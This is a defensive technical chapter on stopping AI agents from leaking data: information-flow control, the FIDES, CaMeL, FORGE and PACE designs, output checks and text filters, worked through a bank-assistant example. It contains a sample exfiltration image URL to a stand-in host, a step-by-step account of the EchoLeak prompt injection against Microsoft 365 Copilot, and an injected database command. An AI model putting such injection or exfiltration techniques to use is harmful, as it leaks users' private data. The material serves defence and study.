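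Many rules depend on only a few features of the context, which code can look up. *PROBE* (2026), which trains a model to audit agents, uses 20 policies for a flight-booking assistant. Code can check 16 of them exactly. The other four, including the one on disclosing internal pricing, need a model's judgement. At the bank, R1 and R2 depend mostly on facts that code can check.

The bank can therefore put this fixed core in code and refer the rest to a person. Suppose a customer is in hospital and his daughter asks the assistant for his balance. If he has authorised her, the gate finds the authorisation and allows the request. If he hasn't, the gate holds the request for a member of staff, who can ask questions and take responsibility for the answer. This works if such cases are uncommon. If an agent constantly passed on information from Slack, staff would have to review so many requests that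 approval fatigue would soon set in.

An organisation can also enlarge the fixed core by changing how it collects facts. Missing confirmations accounted for 61% of the calls NOMOS blocked for the airline and 84% of those it blocked for the shop. In τ²-bench the customer confirms by typing "yes" in the chat, so software has to interpret the conversation. If the customer confirmed in an app instead, as under R2, the gate would only need to look up the record.

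## Tracking where data came from before it is sent

Suppose the bank now wants its assistant to pass suspicious cases to the fraud team. The assistant has to read the fraud notes to do this, so the bank can no longer enforce R3 by withholding them. A gate that checks each call separately will let the assistant read a note and send the customer a message, because its job requires both. But if the assistant reads the note before it writes the message, the message may include the note's contents. The bank would then have broken R3 even though every call was allowed. Shane Mac's bank balances reached his company's Slack in much the same way.

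The gate therefore needs a record of what went into the message. In information-flow control, software attaches a label to each piece of data, keeps the label with the data as it moves, and checks the label at every sink, meaning any place where data leaves the system.

### Labels as sets of readers

For a disclosure rule, the most useful label is the set of people who may read the data. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, combine such labels by intersection, because a text that draws on two documents should go only to people who may read both. Data derived from sources with reader sets R₁, …, Rₙ has the reader set

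R = R₁ ∩ … ∩ Rₙ.

A message may go to a set of recipients T only if T ⊆ R, so that every recipient is a permitted reader.

Suppose the customer is called Dana. The bank's labels might be:

- Dana's address and card number: {Dana, support, fraud team}
- the fraud note on her account: {support, fraud team}
- the bank's opening hours: everyone

A message that draws only on Dana's address can go to Dana but not to her neighbour, as R1 requires. A message that draws on both the address and the note has the reader set {Dana, support, fraud team} ∩ {support, fraud team} = {support, fraud team}, so the gate lets it go to the fraud team but not to Dana. The gate doesn't check the wording, so it stops a paraphrase of the note as reliably as an exact copy, unlike a string comparison.

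Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example that involves no attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer his email. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales figures, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see them yet, has written to ask about them. Once the agent has read both emails, its reply has the reader set {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so it can't go to Marco without Alex's approval. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the reply could have gone out automatically.

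Reader sets restrict where data can go, but they don't stop an attacker from steering the agent. A stranger could still use a payment reference to make the assistant send Dana a false warning, since the warning contains nothing she isn't allowed to read. Costa and colleagues therefore add a second label that marks data as trusted or untrusted. Anything derived from untrusted data is also untrusted, and the gate can refuse consequential calls the model makes after reading untrusted text.

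### How one note blocks every later message

A language model reads its whole context at once, so software can't easily trace which parts influenced a given sentence. The safe approach is to assume that all of them did and give everything the model writes the combined label of everything in its context.

This causes severe over-blocking. Once the fraud note enters the context, the assistant's next message has the reader set {support, fraud team}, even if it says only that the branch opens at nine. The gate blocks that message and every later one to Dana until the bank starts a new conversation without the note.

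Costa and colleagues measured the effect with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, a prompt-injection benchmark. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed without an attack. FIDES, in the last row, is their own design.

| Agent | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no label checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary agent, label checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
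| FIDES, label checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

Label checks made the ordinary agent nearly useless on Slack, where most tasks involve reading what other people wrote. They did not reduce its performance on travel tasks, because the policy let it use many of the travel tools even after it had read untrusted text.

### FIDES and data the model handles by name

FIDES reduces over-blocking by keeping restricted data out of the context while still letting the agent use it:

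1. A tool returns a result with a label on each field.
2. If adding a field would make the context's label more restrictive, FIDES stores the field in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name.
3. The model can use that name as an argument in a later tool call. Code replaces the name with the stored value, and the gate checks the value's label.
4. If the model needs something worked out from the hidden text, such as a summary, it can ask a second, quarantined model that has no tools. The answer goes into a new variable with the combined label of everything that went into it.
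5. The model can also open a variable and read it. The context then takes on the variable's label.

At the bank, the assistant could use the fraud note's variable name to forward the note to the fraud team, then tell Dana the opening hours. The gate would allow both messages because the note never entered the context. If the assistant put that variable into a message to Dana, the gate would deny the call.

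Averaged over the four settings, FIDES completed about 50% of tasks, compared with 42% for the ordinary agent with label checks and 84% for the ordinary agent without them. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's lead over the ordinary agent with checks grew from 8 points to 16. Some of the remaining loss comes from GPT-4o confusing variable names, which newer models should do less often. But many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policy is meant to block.

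The ordinary agent without checks was vulnerable to 152 attacks, and FIDES with checks was vulnerable to none. AgentDojo's scorer counted three successful attacks against FIDES, but Costa and colleagues dismissed them after reading the logs. The count of zero also depends on how they chose the labels. They marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, so no attack could arrive through a trusted field. A bank has to label its data without knowing which fields attacks will use.

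The results are also weaker evidence about R3 than about prompt injection. In these tests, FIDES hid only untrusted data in variables, and confidential data stayed visible to the model. The tests therefore did not measure how hiding confidential data that the bank trusts, such as a fraud note written by its own staff, would affect the model's performance.

### CaMeL and the program fixed in advance

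CaMeL (Debenedetti et al., 2025) goes further, because the model that plans the task never reads the data. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which builds on CaMeL, describes the earlier system. A privileged model reads only the user's request and writes a program for the whole task in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter runs the program, which calls a quarantined model with no tools when it needs to extract something from a document. Every value has a label that records where it came from and who may read it, and a policy checks the labels of the arguments before each tool call.

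If a member of the bank's staff asked for Dana's case to be handled, the program might include these lines:

```
address = read_account(dana).address
note    = read_fraud_note(dana)
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise in one line", note)

send(fraud_team, summary)   # {support, fraud team}: allowed
send(dana, address)         # {Dana, support, fraud team}: allowed
send(dana, summary)         # {support, fraud team}: denied
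```

The interpreter can determine that `address` was not derived from `note`, so reading the note doesn't block the message that contains only the address. An instruction hidden in the note could corrupt the summary, but it couldn't add a line to the program.

The drawback is that the planner has to anticipate every action the task might need. The program can branch on a value it extracts, but it can't take an action the planner left out. Costa and colleagues classed 44% of AgentDojo's banking tasks and 43% of its Slack tasks as ones where the right actions depend on what the tools return. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) adds that Python's exceptions and dynamic typing make it hard to check in advance where a program could send information.

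Reports of CaMeL's performance conflict. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), it eliminates nearly all AgentDojo attacks while completing a comparable share of tasks. Li, Wang and colleagues reran it on newer models in *PACE* (2026) and got much worse results. The most damaging group of AgentDojo attacks succeeded 0.3% of the time with Qwen-3.8-27B, 28% with DeepSeek-V4-Flash and 36% with GPT-5.6 Luna. Task completion was 16 to 27 percentage points lower than with an undefended agent.

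Li and colleagues were testing CaMeL as a rival to their own design. In their tests on the WASP benchmark, more attacks succeeded against their rerun of FIDES than against an agent with no defence, with all three models. This looks odd, and they may not have reproduced the older systems faithfully, so their figures are weak evidence against CaMeL.

### FORGE and the graph of causes

FORGE, which first circulated under the name PCAS, works with an existing agent, whereas FIDES and CaMeL require the developer to build the agent in a particular way. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) describes how FORGE records every message, tool call and tool result as a point in a graph, with an arrow from each event to any later event it may have influenced. Before a tool call runs, FORGE traces the arrows backwards from the call and checks the whole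 history against the rules.

The rules are in Datalog, a database language that can follow chains of any length. For R3, the bank could write:

```
HasNote(e) :- ReadsFraudNote(e).
HasNote(e) :- DependsOn(e, d), HasNote(d).
Deny(a)    :- SendsOutsideBank(a), HasNote(a).
```

The first line adds a fraud note to the history of any event that reads it. The second adds the note to the history of every later event that depends on that one, however many steps removed. The third denies any message that has a fraud note in its history and is addressed to someone outside the bank.

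A graph can keep the rule from blocking work that doesn't depend on the notes. Suppose one agent reads the notes and reports only to the fraud team, while another talks to Dana. No arrows lead from the notes to Dana's conversation, so the second agent's messages to her go through. If the first agent passed something to the second, as Mac's finance bot apparently did, arrows would connect the notes to the conversation and the rule would apply. But FORGE treats everything a model writes as dependent on everything in its context, so within a single agent the rule blocks as many harmless messages as a label on the whole context would.

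For prompt injection, Palumbo and colleagues used more permissive rules, which they call a provenance policy. The policy checks whether the user asked for the specific action and whether its target came from an acceptable source, so an agent that has read untrusted text can still make a payment the user requested. They compared this policy with the FIDES policy on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o. In every row of the table, the agent also saw the user's request again after each batch of tool results. The tool filter is a model that picks the permitted tools at the start. The figures are percentages.

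| Protection | Attack success | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Repeated request only | 14.1 | 83.7 | 72.5 |
| Tool filter | 3.1 | 73.4 | 69.5 |
| FIDES's policy, run in FORGE | 0.6 | 33.2 | 34.4 |
| FORGE's provenance policy | 0.9 | 62.5 | 63.8 |

The provenance policy allowed almost twice as many tasks as FIDES's policy, with about the same security. However, the comparison used AgentDojo's standard agent, so it seems to leave out the variables that FIDES uses to limit over-blocking. The provenance policy also doesn't solve the bank's problem with R3. Dana asked for a message and is the right recipient, so only the content is forbidden.

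A smaller test by Palumbo and colleagues comes closer to R3. A GPT-4.1 mini agent had to summarise an outside document that contained instructions to leak a top-secret file. With only a written instruction against leaking, the agent sent the file in all five trials. When a rule blocked outside emails that depended on both untrusted text and sensitive data, the agent never sent the file, and it still sent a harmless internal email every time.

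Datalog rules can also require something to be present in a call's history. In a system of several agents that query a US database of drug labels, one rule required each agent to get a supervisor's approval in its current session. The agents made 40 unapproved queries in 15 trials without the rule and none with it. They still reached the right answer in all 15 trials with the rule, because FORGE returned the reason for blocking a call and the agents then sought approval.

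The guarantee holds only if FORGE monitors every relevant action and records its causes correctly. An unnecessary arrow causes extra blocking, while a missing one lets data out unnoticed. In the AgentDojo test, FORGE checked tool calls but not the agent's final reply. Excluding calls that FORGE had blocked, all the successful attacks were in that reply. FIDES also exempts replies to the user by default. This is reasonable when the user owns the data, but Dana isn't entitled to see everything her assistant reads, so the bank would have to check each reply to her as it would any other message.

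### What PACE adds

PACE (October 2026) runs two checks before each tool call. The path check searches a graph for routes from protected data, or from text an attacker may have written, to a harmful effect. It then finds a minimum cut that breaks those routes, which in practice usually means blocking the call. The authority check lists the call's concrete effects and compares them with permissions that code derives from the user's request.

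Li and colleagues tested the checks separately on a subset of AgentDojo with Qwen-3.8-27B. Without protection, 37.4% of attacks succeeded and the agent completed 76.8% of its tasks. The path check alone stopped every attack but cut task completion to 13.6%. The authority check alone also stopped every attack, and the agent completed 64.6% of its tasks. The full system, which also adjusts how it blocks or repairs calls, reached 67.2% task completion.

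PACE avoids most of the over-blocking by letting the authority check override the path check, but this weakens the mathematical guarantee. Li and colleagues prove that data can't travel along the routes the path check has cut, as long as the cut stays in place. The guarantee holds for a strict version of PACE, but all their experiments use a version that can restore a blocked call.

Most attacks in these benchmarks try to get the agent to do something the user never asked for, which a check on authority is well suited to catching. The figures may therefore understate the value of tracking where data came from. When the action is authorised and only the content is forbidden, as with R3, the gate needs a record of the content's origin. Even PACE's graph can miss forbidden content, because it detects protected values that someone has copied or re-encoded in certain standard ways, but not ones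 that a model has paraphrased or translated.

### Tracking rows inside a database

Labels and graphs can only approximate what influenced a model's output. A database computes each row of a result from particular rows of its tables, so the row can be traced to its sources without guessing. In *Data Flow Control*, Summers and Wu (2026) of Columbia University use this to write rules about which records may contribute to a result.

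Suppose a bank analyst's agent wants to publish average balances by postcode. Each balance has its own reader set, and the intersection of thousands of those sets contains only bank staff, so reader labels would never allow the bank to publish the average. The bank can instead write a rule about how the data was combined:

```
SOURCE Accounts
CONSTRAINT COUNT(DISTINCT Accounts.customer) >= 50
ON FAIL REMOVE
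```

The rule applies to any query that reads the accounts table. It removes any result row based on fewer than 50 customers, such as a row for a postcode with three customers. The bank would need an exception so that Dana can see her own record. Summers and Wu's rules allow such exceptions because they can refer to other tables, such as a list of users and their roles.

A software layer called Passant enforces the rules by rewriting each query before it runs. For this rule, it would add a count of distinct customers to each row, filter out rows that fail the rule, and then remove the count. Recording the full history of every row can slow a query by a factor of 10,000 or more, according to *Agentic Data Environments* (2026). Passant computes only what the rule needs, and on five database systems it added almost nothing to the average running time.

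DAPLab, the Columbia group behind this work, also tested whether a language model could do the checking. The rule allowed a tax agent to deduct at most 50% of a meal's cost. GPT-5.5 and a Claude Opus model each received the rule, a database query and its results, and had to classify the query as breaking the rule or not. Each setting used ten queries, half of which broke the rule. The best accuracy was 50%, which GPT-5.5 reached by rejecting every query.

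This test was small, with only ten queries per setting. It was also hard to pass because, as DAPLab points out, the models couldn't see how the data had flowed through the query, which the rule depends on. In another experiment, Summers and Wu asked GPT-5.2 whether each of 1,000 updates followed a short list of allowed status changes. It judged all of them correctly but took about a hundred times as long as Passant. A model can apply a simple rule when it has the facts, but code usually can too, and much faster.

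Passant protects data only within a single query. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (2025), an earlier paper on the same approach, warns that a sequence of queries can break a rule that no individual query breaks. For example, if the agent copies account data into a temporary table and then queries that table, the rule above no longer applies. The database also can't track a value once the model has read it. *Environment Steering* (2026) begins to extend the method to agents, with a rule that an agent may reveal only the user's own private data. Such rules can use a model to judge what a text means. The check always runs, but the model's judgement can be wrong.

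### Deliberate release

Labels only get stricter as data combines, so a usable system needs a way to relax them. In declassification, someone with authority over a piece of data deliberately allows a new reader to see it. For example, the fraud team might want to tell Dana that it has blocked a payment. That fact comes from the note, so the gate would stop the message. The bank would have to amend R3 to let the fraud team release a statement the team has approved, and the gate would then add Dana to that statement's readers.

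The authority should belong to whoever is responsible for the data, here the fraud team. Dana can't have it, because R3 exists partly to keep the notes from customers. The model can't have it either, or an attacker could get the note released by persuading the model.

Microsoft's account includes a sample rule that shows how easily this can go wrong. The rule governs posts to a Teams channel, and it works in this order:

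1. If the agent wrote the post in a trusted context, allow it.
2. Otherwise, if every member of the channel may read the content, allow it.
3. Otherwise, ask the user, and list the people who would gain access.

The first step skips the reader check. Costa and colleagues argue that if the context contains no untrusted text, nobody can have tricked the agent, so the release is presumably intentional. Skipping the check may be acceptable when an employee shares her own documents, but it would defeat R3 at the bank, because FIDES treats the user's messages as trusted by default and the bank's own staff wrote the fraud notes. If Dana asked for the notes, the context would be trusted and the rule would allow the reply. The rule also does not prevent mistakes an agent makes without being tricked, and Mac said that nobody had asked for the post about his finances.

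FIDES can also release information automatically. It can restrict the quarantined model to answering yes or no, and the policy can accept that answer where it would reject free text. This leaves an attacker little room to pass on instructions, although a single "yes" can reveal whether Dana is under investigation. The 50-customer threshold in the bank's database rule is also a kind of automatic release, but it is easier to review because a person chooses the number once and code applies it every time.

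Declassification is the weakest point of all these designs because a mistaken release undoes every earlier check. The gate cannot detect the mistake because its records show that someone with authority approved the message. Over-blocking increases the risk, since every harmless message the gate stops gives the fraud team another request to review and makes approval fatigue more likely. Costa and colleagues mention that a system could upgrade a document to trusted after a classifier finds no sign of prompt injection, but they warn that relying on such detectors can weaken the guarantees. An attacker would then only need to fool the classifier.

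### Use at the end of 2026

By the end of 2026, information-flow control for agents was available to developers but still mostly experimental. Microsoft has gone furthest towards putting it into products. GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal, can track labels for some tools if the user turns on an experimental flag. Microsoft's Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, includes a security module with labels, variables and a quarantined model. GitHub's connector for agents can label the content it returns as untrusted if it comes from a public repository and as private if it comes from a private one.

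The other designs are further from ordinary use. FORGE is open source. Palumbo and colleagues have tried it on the coding agent in VS Code and on OpenClaw, a personal assistant, where they used it to stop private information from passing between agents through shared memory. Columbia's software is also open source, and DAPLab was talking to its first industry partners about using it in their products. Li and colleagues have released PACE's code, but the version they tested lacks the parts needed to recover safely from a crash. *Operationalizing CaMeL* is largely a list of changes CaMeL would need before companies could rely on it.

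Much of the remaining work is labelling. To connect a new set of tools through Microsoft's open-source gateway, a developer must describe the format of each tool's results, write a function that carries labels from the tool's inputs to its outputs, and choose or write a policy for it. Few tools come with even a description of their result format, according to the count cited by Millstone and colleagues.

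## Checking output that a browser, database or program will act on

In the AgentDojo test of FORGE, the attacks that succeeded were in the agent's final reply, which FORGE didn't check. A gate on tool calls leaves this route open, because other software also acts on what a model writes. A chat window loads an image from an address in the reply, a database runs a query, and a shell (the program that carries out typed commands) runs a command line. The query or command may arrive inside a permitted tool call, but permitting a tool called `run_query` doesn't check the query itself.

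*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) advises developers to treat model output as untrusted until code has checked it. OWASP listed failing to do so as "insecure output handling" among its 2023 risks for language-model applications, and renamed it "improper output handling" in 2025.

### How loading an image sends data

Suppose an instruction in a stranger's payment reference gets the bank's assistant to add an image to its reply to Dana. The image has this made-up address:

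```
https://pictures.example/dot.png?note=14-Mill-Lane
```

The first part names a server, the middle names a file, and the part after the question mark is extra text for the server. When Dana's app displays the reply, it requests the file from pictures.example and sends the extra text, which contains her street address. Servers commonly log the web addresses that people request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out, and the attacker can read the log later.

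The server can return a one-pixel image or nothing, so Dana sees at most a broken image. Her browser may have sent her address before she has read the first sentence. An ordinary link can send the same data, but only if she clicks it.

A bank that already labels its data can treat such an image as a sink. Microsoft suggests treating a link to any host that isn't on an approved list as a public channel. Only Dana, support and the fraud team may read Dana's address, so the gate would block the reply. The checks below don't need labels because they restrict the form of the output.

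### Parsing the output into a strict schema

A schema lists the fields that output may contain and the values each field may take. The bank can require the assistant to write every reply as a record with a text field and an optional link field. The link must be one of a few names, such as `branch_page` or `lost_card_page`, so the model has no field for an address of its own. Code parses the reply, rejects anything that doesn't fit the schema, and looks up the real address for the name.

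The parser has to reject unknown fields as well as wrong values. If it ignores an unexpected `image` field but passes the whole record to the app, the app might display the image anyway. It is safer to build a new record from the approved fields and discard the original.

A loose format needs much more inspection than a strict one. *AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) describes a gateway that checks tool calls against rules written in JSON Schema, a standard language for describing the structure of JSON data. An attacker can bury text inside many layers of nested fields, so the gateway collects text from the first 32 layers and flags any deeper call as suspicious. In the paper's tests, it found harmful text 9 and 20 layers down and flagged a call with 50 layers. The bank's reply format has only one layer, so any reply with nested fields immediately fails the schema check.

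A schema can confirm that the link field contains `branch_page`, but not that Dana asked about a branch. It also can't restrict the text field much, because an ordinary answer to a customer has no fixed form. Reddy and Gujral suggest constraining the model to produce the right format as it writes. This would prevent some rejected replies, but the text field would still need to be handled separately.

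### Escaping and stripping markup

Web pages use HTML, in which certain characters give the browser instructions. The character `<` begins a tag, and one kind of tag loads an image. Escaping replaces these characters with codes that the browser displays as ordinary characters. If the assistant writes an image tag in its text field and the tag is escaped, Dana sees the tag as text and her app doesn't request the image.

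Many chat apps also accept Markdown, a simpler notation that they convert to HTML. An app that escapes HTML before converting Markdown can still create an image from Markdown in the reply. The bank can avoid this by displaying the assistant's text as plain text.

If customers need bold type and lists, the app can convert the Markdown to HTML and then strip every element that isn't on a short allowlist. Searching the raw text for links is less reliable, because the code must cover every way of writing one. Reddy and Gujral suggest allowing links, emphasis and plain images. But a plain image is enough for the example above to work, so the bank should also remove images or restrict where they can come from.

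The right escaping depends on which program will use the text. A database can safely store an image tag in a customer comment, but the tag may load an image when an employee opens the comment in a browser. Each program that displays or runs stored text therefore has to escape it for that use.

Escaping also doesn't remove a web address written as ordinary text. Some apps turn such text into a link, or fetch a preview of the page, after escaping, so the bank has to switch those features off for the assistant's replies.

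### EchoLeak and the limits of a domain list

An allowlist names the destinations that output may contact. Code can check each link in a reply against the list. The browser can also enforce an allowlist through a content security policy, a set of restrictions that a website sends with its page. The browser then blocks images from hosts that aren't on the list, however the model wrote the link.

EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) got past both kinds of check in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that searches an employee's mail, files and chats. The security company Aim Security found the flaw and reported it to Microsoft in January 2025. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) gives the researchers' account.

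The attack began with a long email from outside the company. It covered common office topics so that Copilot would retrieve it for many different questions. Its instructions appeared to address the human recipient and never mentioned AI, which got them past Microsoft's classifier for prompt injection. When the recipient later asked Copilot a question that brought the email into its context, the instructions told it to put the most sensitive information it could find into a web address.

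Copilot removed outside links written in the usual Markdown notation from its replies, but its filter missed links written in Markdown's other notations. The researchers first got a link through, which the employee would have had to click, and then an image, which the browser would try to load automatically.

The browser's content security policy blocked images from the attacker's server. But its list of allowed addresses had about 30 entries, many of which covered whole families of Microsoft addresses. One entry covered a Teams service that would fetch any outside address given to it. The image therefore pointed to Teams, which passed the request and the data on to the attacker.

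The researchers had already found another route through SharePoint, Microsoft's service for hosting company sites. It used a site the attacker had set up on Microsoft's domain, though the employee would have had to accept an invitation to that site. A domain name identifies who runs a service, but it doesn't show who controls each page or where the service sends requests. An allowlist entry is safe only if the host doesn't relay requests to other addresses and outsiders can't read what it receives.

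Copilot couldn't send email on its own, and Microsoft says it requires user approval for actions that could send content out. Neither restriction prevents a leak when the browser sends the data while displaying the answer.

According to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*, Microsoft said that nobody had exploited the flaw in the wild and that customers didn't need to do anything. Aim Security gave its severity as 9.3, which is critical. "Zero-click" slightly overstates how little the attack required, because the employee still had to ask Copilot something that brought up the email, though a wide range of ordinary questions would have done that.

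According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft made its first repairs in April 2025 and completed the fix on its servers in May, and public disclosure followed on 11 June. They say Copilot now strips embedded images and the overlooked kind of link from incoming outside content. The patches also reportedly added options to restrict outside communication. This account is second-hand, because Reddy and Gujral worked only from public material. Cleaning the incoming email is only a partial remedy, since a model can compose a link from an address that the email describes in words.

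In an account of its defences published that July, Microsoft says it blocked leaks through Markdown images after a report by the researcher Johann Rehberger, then took similar steps against "certain untrusted links". It also says it looks for variants of each reported flaw. The account doesn't name EchoLeak.

Ravia considers EchoLeak mainly a prompt injection, while Reddy and Gujral classify the link filter's failure and the Teams relay as insecure output handling. Both descriptions are accurate, since the attack began with prompt injection and extracted data through unchecked output. But the relay was an ordinary software flaw that Microsoft could fix without solving prompt injection.

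Reddy and Gujral also tabulate which defences they expect to work. They mark a strict content security policy as sufficient to prevent the zero-click leak, but they ran no experiments. Copilot did have a content security policy, so whether one prevents the leak depends on how strict its list of allowed sources is.

Checkmarx, which sells software security tools, reports that Microsoft Copilot Chat and Google Gemini could also leak data through image requests. It suspects that most agents have similar problems.

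*Defender for Office 365 Protects M365 Copilot Chat* (Miller, 2025) describes another layer that Microsoft added in June 2025. Copilot Chat checks a site's reputation when the user clicks a link and warns them if the site is questionable. This check doesn't affect images that load without a click, and an attacker's new domain may not have a bad reputation yet.

### Checking the exact address

An agent that browses the web can't work from a short list of allowed destinations. Long lists are risky too, according to OpenAI, because many legitimate sites redirect visitors to other addresses. If code checks only the first address, an attacker can use a trusted site to redirect the agent to their own server.

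Reddy and Gujral recommend following these redirects before showing a link. But a checker that automatically follows a redirect makes the request that leaks the data, so it should stop after each response, compare the next address with the list, and contact that address only if it passes.

OpenAI's solution is to ask whether the exact address was already public. A separate program explores the web like a search engine and records the addresses it finds, without access to anyone's conversations or accounts. When ChatGPT is about to load an address automatically, code looks for it in that index:

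1. If the exact address is there, the agent may load it.
2. If it isn't, the system tells the agent to try another site, or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

The URL containing "14-Mill-Lane" would almost certainly fail this check. The attacker's site might well be in the index, but the URL ending in Dana's street address did not exist until the model wrote it. The check therefore doesn't need to recognise private data, so encoding the street address would not help the attacker.

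The choice of address can still carry information, even when every address is already public. If an attacker publishes N pages, waits until all of them are in the index, and then gets the agent to load the one that matches a secret, the request reveals log₂ N bits. With 10,000 numbered pages, a single request could reveal the last four digits of a card. The attacker would need time and a compliant model, and limiting how many unfamiliar pages an agent loads would reduce the leak but not eliminate it. OpenAI claims only that the check stops data from leaking through the address itself, and treats it as one layer among several.

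The check also stops some harmless links. A private document or a personalised booking page would not normally be in a public index, so the user gets a warning. OpenAI argues that frequent warnings about unlisted sites would cause approval fatigue, but its own warnings could also cause it for people who often work with private links.

OpenAI has since extended this mechanism, which it calls Safe Url, beyond links in a chat. According to OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection*, it covers pages and bookmarks in the Atlas browser, and pages and searches in Deep Research, a tool that writes reports from web sources. Searches are covered because a query also sends text to another company. When the system detects that information from the conversation would go to a third party, it either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request. Small applications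 that the agent builds in ChatGPT run in a sandbox that asks for the user's consent to unexpected communications.

### Queries and commands built from templates

Yuan and colleagues give an example in which a user asks an agent to summarise customer feedback. An instruction hidden in the feedback causes the model to write a database query that would read the table of users and then delete the audit log. The database runs the query if the application passes it on without checking it.

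Yuan and colleagues' gateway checks for such attacks using 22 text patterns, seven of them for database queries. It blocked all 48 attacks in a test set drawn from known techniques. It also blocked 6 of 500 harmless calls, all six of them queries with OR in a condition. Attackers and honest programmers both use OR to widen queries, and a text pattern isn't enough to distinguish their purposes. Yuan and colleagues acknowledge that their rules may miss new kinds of attack.

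A parameterised query removes the need to guess. The programmer writes the query in advance and leaves a gap for each value:

```
SELECT opening_hours FROM branches WHERE branch_id = ?
```

The model supplies only the branch number. The database receives the query and the value separately, and never interprets the value as part of the command. If the model supplies "218; delete the audit log", the database searches for a branch with that entire string as its number and finds none. This defence against SQL injection still works when a language model supplies the value.

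A parameterised query will return any customer's record if it is given that customer's account number, so the number still has to come from the login session. Templates also limit the assistant to questions that somebody anticipated. That is fine for a support desk, but an analyst may need an agent that writes new queries. In that case, the bank can give the agent a login that can only read certain tables, and use a layer such as Passant to rewrite each query to obey the disclosure rules.

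Shell commands allow the same approach. An application can run one named program and pass the model's text to it as a single argument, instead of giving the shell a whole line to interpret. Microsoft's *CVE-2026-42824* records a later Copilot flaw in this general class, called command injection. Copilot failed to neutralise special elements in a command, which allowed an unauthorised attacker to disclose information over a network. Microsoft says it has fully mitigated the flaw. Even when passed separately, an argument can be unsafe for the program that receives it, so the application still needs to check, for instance, that a file name points inside the permitted folder.

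### Generated code without network access

Some agents write whole programs, for example to turn a year of transactions into a chart. Developers can't write templates for these programs in advance, and scanning the code for signs of misuse has the same weakness as searching queries for patterns. The application can instead run each program in a sandbox with no network connection, no credentials, and only the files the task requires. Microsoft says it prevents Copilot from running "unconstrained and unsandboxed code", though it presents this mainly as protection against attackers who want to run programs on its systems.

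Without a network connection, the program can't send the transactions anywhere itself, whatever its code contains. But the result that the sandbox returns can include the data. If the program returns its chart as a web page, the page might contain the image address from the first example, which Dana's browser would load outside the sandbox. The bank therefore has to check the result like any other output. A chart returned as pixels is safer than one returned as HTML, because a browser doesn't load further addresses from pixels.

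Developers often reopen the connection so that programs can download software packages. That brings back the problem with allowed domains, since a site that distributes packages may also accept uploads from strangers. The bank can avoid this by installing the packages the program needs before running it.

### The bank's reply to Dana

Suppose Dana asks where she can collect her new card, and the assistant's reply should include a link to the branch's page. The bank requires this format:

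```
text:    "You can collect your card from Friday."
link:    branch_page
branch:  218
```

Code checks that the record has only these fields, that `branch_page` is an approved name, and that the bank's table lists branch 218. It builds the address from a fixed template and 218. It then escapes the text and sends the reply to Dana's app, which displays the text without formatting. The app's policy allows images only from one bank server, which holds fixed files and doesn't forward requests.

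Suppose text in the payment reference has led the assistant to try to send Dana's street to pictures.example. If the assistant puts the whole web address in the link field, the reply fails the check because the address isn't an approved name. The street fails in the branch field because it isn't a branch number, and an added image field fails because it doesn't fit the schema. If the assistant puts an image tag in the text field, Dana's app displays the tag as plain text and doesn't load the image.

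When a reply fails the check, the app shows a fixed apology and the bank logs the rejected text. The apology should not quote that text, because it might then display the image that the check blocked. The log viewer also needs to escape the text, because the bank's staff will open the log in a browser.

The assistant could still choose the wrong branch, but the request would go to the bank's own server and disclose nothing to anyone else. The text field is harder to control, because a sentence that asks Dana to phone a stranger's number, or that paraphrases a fraud note, contains no markup and fits the schema. The bank therefore needs a filter that judges what the text means.

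## Filtering the text that people read

Some disclosures occur only in the text of a reply, such as one telling Dana that the fraud team suspects her of lending out her card. Label tracking could block that reply, but it would also block every harmless reply the assistant wrote after reading the note. A text filter is meant to be more selective by checking each reply's wording before Dana sees it.

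### Known secrets and marker strings

The simplest filter compares the reply with a list of strings that must never appear, such as passwords and access keys. A long random password almost never turns up by chance, so this filter raises very few false alarms.

A fraud note usually contains no such string, but the bank can add one by putting a random marker, such as `FN-7Q2X-K81D`, at the top of every note. If a marker appears in a reply to a customer, the assistant has almost certainly copied from a note. The assistant could still leak a note without triggering this check by copying only the sentences below the marker.

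Apps usually display a reply in pieces as the model writes it, and a password might start in one piece and end in the next. If the longest secret on the list has 40 characters, the filter has to hold back the latest 39 until more text arrives. It also has to ignore spacing and capitalization, or a password spelled out letter by letter will pass. Even then, it won't catch a password the model writes backwards.

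### Patterns for card numbers

A pattern describes what a secret looks like, so the bank doesn't have to list every one. For most card numbers, the pattern is sixteen digits, with or without spaces.

Order numbers and tracking codes can also have sixteen digits, but the filter can discard most of them because the last digit of a card number is a check digit. Starting from the right, the filter doubles every second digit, subtracts 9 from any result above 9, and adds up all the digits. A valid card number gives a multiple of 10. For example, 4111 1111 1111 1111, a number programmers use for testing, gives 30. A random sixteen-digit number passes one time in ten, so the check removes about 90% of these false alarms.

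Because R1 allows Dana to see her own card number, the filter should compare any number it finds with the card number on the signed-in customer's account and block it only if the two differ.

### Blocking text copied word for word

A filter can protect longer text by blocking any reply that contains *n* consecutive words from it. If *n* is too small, the filter blocks replies that contain common phrases such as "please contact us if you". If *n* is too large, the model can copy most of a note and still pass the filter by changing a word here and there.

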